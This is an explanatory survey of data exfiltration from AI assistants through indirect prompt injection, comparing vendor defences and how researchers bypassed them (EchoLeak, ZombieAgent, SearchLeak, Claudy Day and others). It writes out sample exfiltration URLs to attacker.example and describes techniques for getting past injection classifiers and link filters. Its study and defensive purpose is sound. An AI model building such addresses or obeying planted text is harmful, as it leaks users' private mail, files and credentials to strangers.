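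An attack on the coding agent Devin, described by Chang and colleagues, is only an apparent counterexample, because the attacker still needed Devin to leak a server's address. Planted text on one web page made Devin set up a small web server that offered Devin's files. A second page made Devin open that server to the internet and told it to leak the address. The attacker could then fetch the files, so the data left in response to an incoming request.

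Attackers need a way to send data out, which also helps explain why injection sources are more varied than exfiltration channels. Each time a company connects its assistant to mail, tickets or code, it adds another place where a stranger can write. Many of these connections are read-only, so they don't add another way to send data out. An image in a reply leaks data the same way in an email assistant as in a code editor. This explains why there are few channels, but not why images rank first.

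### Images load without asking

Chat apps commonly load images automatically, whereas links need a click, so an attacker who can use either has good reason to prefer the image. If this default explains the cluster, images should dominate while assistants can only display text, then make up a smaller share of exploits once assistants get tools.

The table by year is consistent with this. The products under attack changed in the same period. Brodt and colleagues' three incidents from 2023 involved assistants that read web pages and a model that read images. Of their 21 incidents from 2025 and January 2026, seven involved coding assistants and three involved agents that operate a computer. By then researchers had more tools to abuse, and they used them in their exploits.

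As far as the disclosures show, ten of the 15 image exploits faced no allow-list of image domains. In the other five (Bard, Writer, EchoLeak, ForcedLeak and Superhuman), the vendor had an allow-list, but researchers found a way to send data through a permitted domain. Default image loading therefore directly explains about two thirds of the image exploits. The other five show that researchers kept trying images after vendors had restricted them.

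Link previews complicate the explanation. Slack also fetches posted links by default and without a click, yet previews appear only once in the count. This may be because a preview leak requires an assistant that posts in a messaging app and a developer who left previews on, whereas nearly every assistant has a chat window. Researchers may also have looked for preview leaks less often. When PromptArmor invited people to test such assistants in 2026, several combinations of agent and app leaked data.

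A proper test would require knowing how many assistants researchers examined without finding a leak. Researchers rarely publish such results, though WithSecure did report that image leaks failed against Gemini. Without them, the 15 image exploits could mean either that most apps load images unsafely or that researchers tried image leaks on nearly every app.

### Bug programmes and proof of harm

Many vendors run bug bounty programmes, which pay outsiders for reporting flaws. A vendor is more likely to accept a report as a security problem if it includes a server log with a customer's secret in it than if it only shows a planted sentence making an assistant write something odd. A researcher who wants a reward therefore has a reason to keep going until data comes out. Given this incentive, we would expect exploits to end in something a vendor must recognise as harm, such as stolen data or commands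 run on someone's computer. The incentive doesn't favour any channel, because a request from an image proves the theft as well as a request from a tool.

Brodt and colleagues' table fits this prediction. In 25 of its 36 entries the attacker steals data or runs code, and only three entries describe attacks that just change or elicit text. But anyone choosing prominent incidents for a table would also prefer the harmful ones, whatever the researchers' motives.

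Vendors' decisions on actual reports fit less well, because vendors have often paid nothing for demonstrated theft. Google's bug programme page for Antigravity lists data exfiltration and code execution through its browser agent as "known issues", which makes them ineligible for a reward. When another researcher reported that Antigravity leaked data through images, Google called this intended behaviour. Anthropic didn't pay for the gap in `web_fetch`, saying that it had already found the problem. Logue's diagram leak fell outside Microsoft's programme, and xAI closed Rehberger's Grok reports as "Informational". However, Atlassian paid $6,000 for RovoBlast, and Google paid for the leak in Vertex AI.

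Three separate parties published leaks or related flaws in Antigravity within about a week in November 2025, which suggests that rewards didn't guide researchers' choice of product, though they may have started work before they knew of Google's exclusion. Some researchers have other reasons to publish. PromptArmor, Varonis and Radware sell security services and gain from the attention, and Rehberger said that he published the Grok flaws to raise awareness. Proof of harm matters to all of them, with or without a reward. That may explain why they show stolen data, but it can't explain why the data leaves through images.

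### Techniques that worked before

Researchers may also first try techniques that have worked before, and the archive gives some support for this. Rehberger reported or co-reported ten of the 29 exploits and PromptArmor reported six, so these two account for more than half. Nine of their 16 exploits used an image, compared with six of the other 13.

The two shares are close, so the preference for images isn't peculiar to two prolific researchers. But the others may have learned the method from the same blogs. The researcher who reported Antigravity's image leak used a method that Willison called "an old classic".

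Researchers also have reason to reuse an outbound step, such as an image, and spend their time on the wording of the planted text. The outbound step works every time in an app that allows it, while the planted text is much less reliable. *SoK* (Damianakis and Psounis, 2026) merged twenty public collections of injections and found that only about 2% of the distinct entries from two public contests had achieved their aim.

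Damianakis and Psounis also analysed 13 disclosed incidents by how the attacker built the planted text. No incident needed more than three of their six kinds of construction, and all 13 used plain instructions. Many of the attacks depended on how the text reached the model or how the app displayed the result, including images written in Markdown. They caution that the set is small and leans towards systems with tools.

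People who plant instructions on web pages also copy each other heavily. Khodayari and colleagues grouped their 15,387 injections by wording into 363 templates, and 54 of these covered 95% of the injections. Most of the injections weren't attempts at theft, so this shows only how easily such text spreads.

Copying can't fully explain the clustering, though. Rehberger published his preview tests in 2023 and again in 2024, but the archive has only one entry for that channel. A published technique spreads only if enough products allow it. If researchers were only copying, they would also have kept using images where a tool was available, but the table shows them moving to tools from 2025.

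PromptArmor's disclosures show how researchers choose an exfiltration channel. PromptArmor knew throughout how to send data out through images and through uploads to an allowed domain, and each time it used the channel the product left open. Willison wrote up two of its disclosures on 12 and 14 January 2026. Superhuman still allowed images from a Google domain, so PromptArmor used an image. Claude Cowork let its agent contact only a short list of domains, including Anthropic's own, so PromptArmor had the agent upload the files there. Four months later, PromptArmor used images against Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which would display them in a message to the user.

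## How do vendors close an outbound channel?

PromptArmor's choice of channel depended on which ones each vendor had closed. A vendor closes a channel by restricting the requests that the model's text or tool calls can cause. The fixes below run from the loosest, which lets an assistant contact any address if the user agrees, to the strictest, which cuts the assistant off from the network. Stricter fixes stop more thefts but also remove more of what people use an assistant for.

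Most of these fixes are deterministic: ordinary software applies a fixed rule and gives the same result however persuasive the planted text is. A model's refusal or a classifier's verdict on an email is probabilistic. Microsoft advises organisations to expect some injections to succeed and to combine both kinds of defence. In its own products, Microsoft (2025) uses hardened standing instructions and classifiers against the planted text. Its measures to limit the damage if those fail include deterministically blocking known exfiltration methods.

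### Asking the user first

A confirmation prompt holds a request until the user approves it. Anthropic added a simple version to Claude in 2023, the "Show Image" button. Google listed a "user confirmation framework" among Gemini's defences in June 2025. Cyber Security News cites Outlook's "Draft with Copilot" feature as an example of Microsoft requiring consent before a risky action.

When OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, works on a developer's own computer, it asks before running a command that needs the network, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. For connectors to other services, it uses each tool's label to decide whether to ask. It can ask about a tool whose label mentions side effects, and it always asks about one labeled "destructive". A tool with a wrong or missing label could therefore run without Codex asking.

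A confirmation prompt covers only the actions the vendor chose to ask about. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork asked for confirmation before emailing other people but not before messaging its own user, and PromptArmor's attack used that exception.

The user also has to judge the request. If Anna's mail app had shown her the image address that the delivery notice produced, she would have seen an unfamiliar domain followed by 400 characters of Base64, with no sign that they were a supplier's quotation. If the app asked her often, she would probably stop reading the prompts. OpenAI says of its own warnings that frequent false alarms can train people to click through them. Microsoft's guidance calls the human check the last line of defence, which seems right. A prompt works best when it appears rarely because another rule has already let the harmless requests through.

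### Fetching through the vendor's server

An image proxy is a server that fetches images for the user. The app rewrites each image address so that the browser contacts the vendor's server, which downloads the image and passes it on. Webmail services commonly do this to hide their users from newsletter senders.

With a proxy, the attacker's log would show the vendor's server instead of Anna's network address and browser. But the vendor's server would still request the address that the model wrote, so the 400 characters would still be in the log. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* makes the same point about any permitted server that fetches addresses for the browser. A proxy can also weaken a Content Security Policy (CSP), because the browser contacts only the vendor's own domain, which the policy allows.

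A proxy by itself protects the user's identity but not the data. It still gives vendors one place to put a check that covers every app. It can also cache each image for a few minutes, so that repeat requests for the same address during that time don't reach the attacker.

### Lists of permitted domains

A website sets a CSP with a line such as this, which it sends along with the page:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.vendor.example`

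Here `img-src` means the rule covers images, and `'self'` stands for the website's own domain. Because attacker.example isn't on this list, the browser blocks the image and Anna sees a broken picture. The browser applies the rule however an image tag got onto the page, so a CSP also stops an image inside a diagram that the page draws.

Users can't see images from sites outside the list, such as photographs of a hotel the assistant has recommended. The vendor also has to keep the list short and up to date. By early 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot had both a CSP and a filter that removed links from replies, and *EchoLeak* (2025) describes how researchers bypassed both.

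Salesforce corrected its list of allowed domains after the ForcedLeak attack, in which researchers registered an expired domain that was still on the list. Because a CSP for images doesn't stop clicked links, Salesforce also added Trusted URLs, which prevents its agents from producing links to domains the company doesn't trust, as Willison reported in September 2025. Any outside site an agent should link to, such as a supplier's, now has to be trusted first.

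Vendors can apply the same kind of list to an agent's tools, enforced by a firewall instead of the browser. GitHub's Copilot cloud agent works on a programming task on a remote machine and proposes its changes in a pull request. A firewall limits its internet access by default, which GitHub says is because of the risk of leaking code. The firewall always permits the servers through which the agent works with GitHub, and by default it also permits a list of other hosts that GitHub recommends.

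Since July 2025, developers have been able to allow more hosts, drop the recommended list or switch the firewall off, according to GitHub's *Configure internet access for Copilot coding agent* (2025). When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request, so reviewers can see that something in the task directed the agent to an unapproved server.

The Bard leak showed that a domain list is safe only if nobody can use a permitted domain to collect data. Willison thinks it is hard to choose domains that meet this condition. The next fix avoids that problem by checking the whole address, not just the domain.

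### Anthropic's rule for web_fetch

Anthropic released `web_fetch` in September 2025 as a tool that developers could add to programs built on Claude. The tool retrieves the text of a web page or PDF. Anthropic's documentation, which Willison quoted that day, said that Claude could not construct addresses for it. The tool would open an address only if that address had already appeared in the conversation, and it had to come from one of these places:

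- a user's message;
- the result of a tool that the developer's own software ran;
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch.

It would not open an address produced by code Claude had run on Anthropic's servers, presumably because a few lines of code can build any address.

Suppose Anna's assistant had this tool, and the delivery notice included an instruction to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` with the quotation added at the end. The first part of the address is in the notice and the quotation is in the supplier's email, but the full address appears nowhere in the conversation, so the tool refuses to open it even if the model tries. The tool could still open an address printed in full in the notice, but the attacker would learn from that request only that an assistant had read the notice.

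Willison found a flaw in the category of "user messages". Many developers whose software calls Claude paste emails and documents into the slot marked for the user's text, so the tool would accept a stranger's URLs as the user's own. He still thought the ban on URLs that Claude constructs itself gave the most protection, because the usual attack depends on constructing one. He also tested the consumer Claude app and found the same restriction.

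Anthropic warned that some risk remained and recommended the tool only for trusted environments or for data that isn't sensitive. Developers who wanted more protection could set `allowed_domains`, which adds a list of permitted domains to the address rule. In 2026 Anthropic narrowed the rule to exclude addresses that the tool found inside fetched pages, after the researcher Ayush Paul had used such addresses to leak a user's details.

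The rule is a small inconvenience for the user. Claude can't open a weather site's page for Lyon by guessing its address, so it has to run a search first and open one of the results.

### OpenAI's Safe Url

OpenAI arrived at a similar rule in stages. In December 2023, it added a check to ChatGPT, internally named `url_safe`, but didn't publish the criteria. Tenable (2025) found that the check covered links as well as images. Rehberger guessed in 2023 that OpenAI's servers might be looking up each address in Bing's index. Tenable found that addresses on bing.com always passed, which gave it a way around the check.

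OpenAI tightened the check around August 2025, which stopped the attacks Rehberger had been demonstrating, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. After Radware's ShadowLeak attack, OpenAI also restricted ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as it had received them. After Radware's ZombieAgent variant, OpenAI further restricted ChatGPT to opening links from emails only if they were in a well-known public index or the user had supplied them, according to a January 2026 press report, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*.

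OpenAI explained the design on 28 January 2026 in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, and in a post by Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell.

#### Why OpenAI rejected lists of trusted sites

Spânu and Shadwell consider a list of well-known websites first and give two reasons against relying on one. One is the open redirect, which an attacker could use by having the model write an address such as this:

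`https://trusted.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/p?d=…`

A check that looks only at the first domain would approve it. The exact-address rule rejects it, because nobody has published that address.

Their other reason is that people visit far more sites than any list contains, so a strict list would produce constant warnings about ordinary pages. Such a list could work for an assistant used by one company's support staff, since its sources are few and known. The objection is stronger for ChatGPT because its users want it to read the whole web.

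#### How the check works

OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that explores the public web as a search engine does and records the addresses it finds. Before ChatGPT fetches an address by itself, to read an article or display a picture, software checks whether the crawler has recorded that exact address.

If the crawler has already found the address, ChatGPT loads it without asking. The reasoning is that the crawler had no information about Anna, so nothing in her mailbox can have influenced what the address contains.

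If the address isn't in the record, the software either tells the agent to try a different site or shows the user a warning titled "Check this link is safe". The warning displays the address, which the user can copy or open.

As far as Rehberger understands the product, ChatGPT makes one exemption. It treats an address that the user types into a message as safe for the rest of that chat. This is reasonable, because the user has chosen to visit that address.

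In March 2026 OpenAI named the mechanism Safe Url and listed where it applies. In Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, it covers the pages the agent visits and the bookmarks the agent creates. In Deep Research it covers searches and page visits. Canvas, where ChatGPT writes small working programs, and the apps inside ChatGPT use a related method. Their code runs in a sandbox, a closed-off environment that detects unexpected communication and asks for the user's consent.

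#### What Safe Url doesn't promise

OpenAI claims only that the design prevents an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself when it fetches something. It does not claim that the page at a known address is trustworthy or free of planted instructions. The January guarantee also doesn't cover other exfiltration channels, such as text typed into a form, a comment on a shared service, or a name lookup of the kind Check Point used.

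The March description differs slightly from the January one. In March, OpenAI said that Safe Url detects when information from the conversation would go to a third party. The January test checks whether an address is already public, which is an indirect sign of whether it would carry such information. A page that a colleague published an hour ago may fail this test even though its address contains nothing private.

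A known address can also leak data, because the model's choice of address can depend on that data. If an attacker has 1,024 public pages and planted text tells the model which page to open for each possible value, each request conveys ten bits (2¹⁰ = 1,024). Rehberger writes that OpenAI's paper acknowledges this type of leak. He suggests that ChatGPT never visit the same address twice in a session, or that it reuse a stored copy, to make it harder to spell out a message from a fixed set of pages. He had not tested whether OpenAI already did this.

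He calls the design a significant improvement. He expects the practical risk to come from inside the company, where a developer building a new feature may not know that the check exists. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API logs unpatched data exfiltration* describes a developer screen that handled images from model output insecurely when PromptArmor reported it.

### Removing images and links

An app can delete outside images and links from the reply, or show them as plain text. Amazon Q, Vertex AI Studio and other products did this after Rehberger's reports. The fix is simple, and the vendor has no list to maintain.

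Google closes the image channel in Gemini. Its *Mitigating prompt injection attacks* lists "markdown sanitization and suspicious URL redaction" as one of five layers of defense. The sanitizer keeps the app from displaying images at outside addresses, and Google Safe Browsing, the company's service for spotting dangerous websites, identifies links to remove (The Hacker News, 2025).

The sanitizer treats every outside image alike, so it doesn't depend on identifying attacker.example as malicious. Safe Browsing has to recognise a link's destination as malicious, and an attacker can register a new domain that nobody has reported yet. Links therefore seem to be the weaker point, though a link also requires a click.

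Google has since added policies on tool chaining to its deterministic layer for Workspace, according to daily.dev. These presumably restrict what an assistant may do with one tool after using another. Google doesn't regard indirect injection as a problem it can solve permanently.

According to Cyber Security News, Microsoft's deterministic blocking covers images inserted through HTML and the generation of malicious links, which Microsoft describes as known methods. The limits of that approach appeared a month after Microsoft's July 2025 post, when Adam Logue reported that Copilot could put a user's emails into the link of a diagram. Microsoft also limits what the assistant can reach. Companies can attach sensitivity labels to their files and set data loss prevention rules in Microsoft Purview, and Copilot takes both into account. These controls leave the channel open but reduce the data an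 attacker can send through it.

Removing links makes an assistant less useful than removing images does, because users who can't follow a link can't easily check whether the assistant has reported a source correctly. Showing the address as text is a compromise, since a determined reader can still copy it, but in messaging apps the developer also has to turn off link previews.

### No network access by default

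An agent that runs code can contact a server in so many ways that some vendors start by cutting off its network access. Codex cloud, which runs OpenAI's coding agent in containers on the company's servers, splits each job into two phases. According to OpenAI's documentation, setup scripts run first, and they can use the network to install the project's packages and read any secrets the developer has configured. The system then removes the secrets and starts the agent, which is offline by default.

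No model reads strangers' text while Codex is online. By the time the model starts reading bug reports and source files, the configured secrets are gone and it has no connection for sending out the code.

An offline agent can't look up documentation or install a package it finds it needs halfway through a task. Developers can therefore turn on internet access for individual environments. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* illustrates the danger of doing so with a bug report asking the agent to run a command that uploads a description of the developer's latest change to an outside server.

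A developer who turns access on chooses a domain list. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI Network Security*, describes the three presets:

- "None", an empty list to which the developer adds each domain;
- "Common dependencies", more than 70 package libraries, code-hosting sites and similar services;
- "All", with no filtering.

The developer can also restrict the agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the request types that read from a server. This would block the upload in OpenAI's example, which uses a POST request. An agent could still add data to the address of a GET request, so the restriction is weak unless the domain list is short. PromptArmor's *Configuring Codex securely across every platform and use case* warns that even "Common dependencies" leaves several ways to get data out.

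Willison called OpenAI's approach sensible in June 2025, mainly because access was off by default. GitHub's agent instead starts with a recommended list enabled, which lets it do more without configuration but gives attackers more to exploit than OpenAI's defaults do.

Since February 2026, OpenAI has put an "Elevated Risk" label on the Codex network setting and on some features of ChatGPT and Atlas. According to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), OpenAI will remove a label once it decides better security has reduced the risk enough for general use.

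### Lockdown Mode

The same announcement introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that closes many of ChatGPT's outbound channels at once. OpenAI first offered it to organisations with Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans, then began offering it to personal accounts and small businesses in June 2026. OpenAI says most users don't need the setting, which it built for people such as executives and security teams.

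In Lockdown Mode, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of web pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. Search results may be out of date or missing. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, ChatGPT also may not display images in ordinary replies and can't download files for analysis. Deep Research and agent mode are off, and users can't give code written in Canvas network access. Users can still upload files and generate images.

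OpenAI says it switched some features off entirely because it could not give strong deterministic guarantees for them. The list of disabled features therefore also shows where OpenAI thinks data might still escape from the normal product, which includes Safe Url.

Connected apps are the difficult part, because an assistant for office work is of little use without them. For personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services, and any action that writes to them, where these conflict with its protections. In larger organisations the administrators decide which apps and actions to allow, and OpenAI grades the risk for them:

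| Access | OpenAI's grading | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Any action in an untrusted app | High | Administrators should enable only apps they trust |
| Writing in a trusted app where outsiders may see the result | High | An attacker could read what the agent wrote |
| Writing in a trusted app where only trusted people see the result | Medium | The action still leaves a trace somewhere |
| Reading in a trusted app | Medium | It sends nothing, but it can supply the data for a theft |
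| Reading from an index that administrators manage | Medium | It can avoid a live request but may still expose sensitive information |

The GitHub attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated would have failed if an administrator had followed the advice on write access and withheld it for public repositories.

Lockdown Mode doesn't stop planted text from reaching the model, so an instruction in an uploaded file or a stored web page can still make an answer wrong. The setting doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, conversation sharing, or network access in Codex. On a personal account, the user can switch it off for a single chat. OpenAI gives no guarantee and lists enabled apps, unforeseen combinations of features, and new techniques as remaining risks.

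### Coverage compared

Most of these fixes don't stop an agent from leaking data through posts on a service it already uses. Only adding a confirmation prompt or removing write access addresses this channel directly.

| Fix | Channels covered | Channels left open |
|---|---|---|
| Confirmation prompt | Any request or message the vendor chose to ask about | Actions the vendor exempted; anything the user approves |
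| Image proxy without an address check | None; it hides only the user's device and network | All |
| Content Security Policy for images | Images, including those in diagrams, on the web page that carries the policy | Clicked links, link previews, tool requests, phone apps with their own display code, permitted domains that can collect data |
| Domain list for links (Salesforce's Trusted URLs) | Links to domains off the list | Links to permitted domains that can collect data; posts on shared services |
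| Domain list for tools (GitHub's firewall, `allowed_domains`) | Tool requests to domains off the list | Uploads, posts and addresses on permitted domains |
| Exact-address rule (Safe Url, `web_fetch`) | Automatic fetches of addresses into which the model has written data | The choice among known addresses; typed text, posts and name lookups |
| Removing images or links | Whichever of the two the app removes | Tool requests, and display features that the filter misses |
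| Turning off link previews | Automatic fetches by the messaging company | Clicks on the same link, and everything outside the messaging app |
| No network access (Codex cloud's default) | Web requests by the agent while it works | Any domain the developer later permits |
| Lockdown Mode | Live browsing, web images, Deep Research, agent mode, Canvas networking and file downloads | Apps that administrators enable; Codex |

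## Why do closed channels reopen?

Researchers have bypassed Content Security Policies, domain lists, link filters and exact-address rules, sometimes within weeks. OpenAI had fixed ShadowLeak, the email attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research, by early August 2025. On 26 September Radware reported a new attack that worked despite the fix.

Software can't reliably recognise when private data is going to a stranger, so each of these defences checks something simpler, such as whether a domain is on a list, whether the model's text contains a link in a familiar format, or whether an address existed before the conversation. An attacker needs a request that passes the check and still delivers the data.

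The disclosed bypasses have three main causes. Some trusted domains accept data from anyone or forward requests to other servers. Some filters parse the model's text differently from the software that displays it. Even when a rule permits only fixed addresses, the assistant can leak data through its choice of which ones to request. Several exploits combine two of these causes.

### EchoLeak and the trusted Teams server

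In early 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot had a CSP, a filter for outside links, and a classifier that scanned incoming text for injections. Ravia (2025) explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* how his team at Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, bypassed all three with one email and got data out.

The team addressed the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI, and the classifier let the email through. They then had to get Copilot to read it. Copilot uses retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). It retrieves the passages in the mailbox that best match the user's question and gives the model only those, so a hostile email must resemble something the user asks about to reach the model.

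Ravia's team therefore wrote one long email that repeated the same instructions under a series of headings, including employee onboarding, human resources questions and leave of absence. They assumed that Copilot would index a long email in pieces, giving the email many chances to match a user's question. In their demonstration, Copilot retrieved the email when the user asked about various topics. The user didn't have to open the email or refer to it. Ravia calls the technique "RAG spraying".

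The instructions told the model to put the most sensitive information from its input into an image address. They also asked the "recipient" never to mention the email, and Copilot's answer didn't cite it as a source. The team got the image past Copilot's filter by writing it in a form of Markdown that the filter didn't recognise. The browser still refused to load it, because the attacker's domain wasn't on the allowlist in Microsoft's CSP.

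Ravia's article reproduces that list, which has 29 different entries, 11 of them covering every subdomain of a domain. The team searched the permitted domains for a service that would contact an outside address on request, and found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for company websites. A SharePoint feature for embedding outside content would fetch any address named in the request. This route worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site, which few people would do.

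A server belonging to Teams did the same thing without an invitation. The model had to write an image address of this general form:

`https://teams-server.example/content?url=https://attacker.example/p?d=…`

The CSP allowed the browser to request the image from the Teams server. The Teams server then requested the inner address on attacker.example, and the stolen data arrived in the attacker's log. The CSP did not block this second request because it governs only what the browser loads. McHugh identifies the Teams service as one that prepares link previews, a feature that also leaks data from messaging apps.

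Willison described the Teams flaw as an open redirect, but in Ravia's account the server fetched the address itself instead of redirecting the browser to it. Ravia says the browser would not have followed a redirect while loading an image. Anyone checking a domain list only for open redirects would have missed this server.

Aim Labs contacted Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft completed its patch in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). The researchers published on 11 June. Microsoft scored the flaw 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft reported no known attacks on customers.

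Aim Labs called EchoLeak the first zero-click AI vulnerability. Rehberger's attack on Bing Chat in 2023 required no click either, but the user had to have the hostile page open. Ravia made the stronger, more specific claim that earlier attacks either relied on the user pointing the assistant at the planted text or could take only limited data.

### Other trusted domains

Google's Bard leaked data through a trusted domain two years before EchoLeak, because anyone could run a program on Google's own addresses. The writing assistant Writer had a similar weakness in 2023. Its CSP allowed images from CloudFront, Amazon's content delivery service, where any customer can get an address and see the requests sent to it.

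The email program Superhuman allowed image requests to docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A Google Form records answers included in a web address, so an image request can submit data to it. In PromptArmor's demonstration, the user asked for a summary of recent mail, and text planted in one email made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of others to the attacker's form. Willison says the stolen emails included financial, legal and medical information, and credits Superhuman with treating the report as urgent and issuing a fix.

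In Google's Antigravity, the weak entry on the browsing agent's default list of allowed sites was webhook.site, a service that gives anyone a temporary address and displays the requests it receives. Programmers use it for testing, which is presumably why it was listed. PromptArmor hid instructions in tiny type on a web page that posed as a programming guide, and the agent followed them and sent login keys and pieces of code to a webhook.site address. Antigravity's default settings blocked the model from opening the file containing the keys, but it read the file with a terminal command instead. Google said it was working to fix this type of leak.

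In ForcedLeak, researchers at Noma Security registered Salesforce's expired domain. They planted text through a web form that companies use to collect enquiries from potential customers. When an employee asked Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents, about the enquiry, the agent put other customers' email addresses into an image URL on that domain. The domain had probably been safe when Salesforce added it to its list of allowed domains, so a single review of the list would not have prevented the leak.

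The companies in these cases had trusted a domain because of who owned it. But the owner of a domain may let the public use it, and a large company's domains host many products, any of which may start to accept public input. Vendors can reduce this risk by listing one folder in the CSP instead of the whole domain, though they then have a longer list to maintain.

### Uploads to Anthropic's own service

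Anthropic lets Claude run code in a sandbox that can contact only a few hosts. One is Anthropic's API, the interface through which developers use Claude. Code in the sandbox has legitimate reasons to contact it. But anyone can open a developer account and use the API to store files in it. Text planted by an attacker can therefore make Claude upload a victim's files to the attacker's account.

Rehberger reported this route on 25 October 2025. Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, according to Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* (2025). Five days later, Anthropic said that this was a mistake in its process and that such leaks were in scope. Its documentation already described the risk and advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it accessed data unexpectedly.

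PromptArmor used the same route in January 2026 against Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for longer tasks on the user's files. In March, Oasis Security used it against the ordinary Claude website, in a chain of three flaws it named Claudy Day. *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) describes a link that opened Claude with a request already typed in. The user saw only a harmless sentence, but pressing Enter also sent Claude instructions hidden in the link. Claude then searched the user's earlier conversations for something sensitive and uploaded it.

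Luz's team first considered sending the stolen text to Anthropic as a prompt under the attacker's account. That would have failed because Anthropic doesn't show account holders the text of the prompts they send. File storage worked, and it accepts files of up to 500 megabytes. The chain required no connected apps, so an attacker could steal the chat history of an ordinary user with no mailbox or file store attached.

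Anthropic fixed the flaw that allowed hidden instructions. According to *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026), a summary updated on 27 May, the company was still addressing the other two flaws, the upload route and an open redirect that could disguise the link as an advertisement for Claude. Oasis Security's later report, *PromptFiction*, describes an attack that used the upload route against Claude's desktop app. By the time of that report, Anthropic had dealt with the disguised advertisement and the flaw that let a link submit a prompt without review, but the report mentions no fix for the uploads.

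A domain list can't close this channel, because the victim's account and the attacker's account use the same domain. The sandbox could reject requests that carry credentials other than the user's, but it would then have to inspect the contents of each request as well as its destination. Anthropic could also cut the sandbox off from the Anthropic API, but that would break the programs that use it legitimately.

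### Filters that parse text differently from the renderer

Copilot's filter missed the EchoLeak image because Markdown has a second way to write links and images. Instead of putting the address straight after the text, a writer can use a label and put the address elsewhere in the document:

`[Report][1]`

`[1]: https://attacker.example/p?d=…`

Copilot's renderer accepted the labelled form for both links and images, but the filter recognised only the usual one. Ravia's team found several shorter variants that also worked.

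A filter of this kind searches the model's text for strings that look like links, so its developer has to anticipate every string that the renderer will convert into one. Rehberger exploited the same weakness in Google AI Studio by having the model write an image in HTML instead of Markdown. The check is more reliable after conversion, when every link and image is an HTML element with its address in a known field. The software can then inspect that field regardless of how the model wrote the link or image. An app that draws diagrams has to run the check after drawing them.

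Timing can also cause a mismatch. Assistants usually display a reply while the model is still writing it, a practice called streaming. If the app cleans up the reply only at the end, the browser may already have requested an image. In 2025 Omer Mayraz showed that GitLab Duo displayed HTML as a reply arrived. Planted text in a GitLab project could make Duo write an image tag whose address contained private source code. GitLab then stopped Duo from displaying such tags if they pointed to outside domains.

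Microsoft had the same problem a year later. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes an attack on the search feature of Microsoft 365 Copilot for companies. The attacker put instructions in the `q` parameter of a link to Microsoft's own site, the method Varonis had used against the consumer version of Copilot. When the victim clicked the link, the instructions made Copilot search the victim's mail and write an HTML image tag with an email's title in the image's address.

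Microsoft's safeguard wrapped Copilot's finished reply in a block that made the browser treat any HTML as plain text. While Copilot was still writing, however, the HTML was live on the page, so the browser reached the image tag and sent the request before the reply was wrapped. The user could see the odd-looking tag only after the data had been sent.

The CSP should still have blocked the request, so SearchLeak also needed a trusted domain. The CSP allowed images from Bing, which can search for pictures similar to one at a given address. To do this, Bing's server fetches the picture. Varonis gave Bing's image search an address on its own server that included the stolen email title, and Bing sent the title to Varonis when it fetched that address. An email title alone can be valuable because many services put sign-in codes there.

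The list Ravia had published a year earlier already included Bing's domains. Microsoft had patched EchoLeak by then, but its CSP still allowed a domain that fetched outside addresses for anyone. Taler recommends that companies check their lists for such domains and clean up HTML when displaying it, even while the reply is streaming.

Microsoft fixed SearchLeak and rated it critical, though its numerical scores were lower, at 6.5 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the National Vulnerability Database, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). Taler stresses that the attack needed all its parts. Without the timing flaw, the image tag would have been plain text, and without Bing, the browser would have blocked the request.

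### ZombieAgent and the alphabet of addresses

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI added a rule that stopped ChatGPT from changing the addresses it was given. *ZombieAgent* explains how Radware got around that rule.

The attacker's email contained a list of complete addresses, one for each letter, one for each digit, and one standing for a space. They looked like this:

`https://attacker.example/a`

`https://attacker.example/b`

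The instructions told ChatGPT to find a piece of private information, convert it to lower case, and open the address for each character in turn. To send the name "Zvika Doe", ChatGPT opened nine addresses, and the attacker read the name from the order of the requests in the server log. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, as in ShadowLeak. The user only had to ask ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail.

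Rehberger had used the same idea against ChatGPT in 2023, and Radware improved on it by numbering the addresses. A request to the address ending in a0 meant the first character was an a, a request to the one ending in a1 meant the second was, and so on. The attacker could then put the characters in order even if the requests arrived out of sequence. A block of ten characters requires 260 addresses for letters and 100 for digits.

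*ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* attributes the flaw to OpenAI not restricting the addition of a single letter to an address. Radware says ChatGPT added nothing, because the email supplied every address in full. If so, a stricter ban on changing addresses would not have helped.

Radware also got around another of OpenAI's restrictions. To keep planted text from making lasting changes, OpenAI had blocked ChatGPT from using its memory in a chat once it had used a connected service such as Gmail. Radware found that the reverse order still worked. A file the user shared could plant an instruction in ChatGPT's memory, and in later chats ChatGPT would read that memory and then open the attacker's email for further instructions. ChatGPT also refused to open addresses stored in its memory, but the addresses used for the leak were in the email. This let the leak continue in every new conversation.

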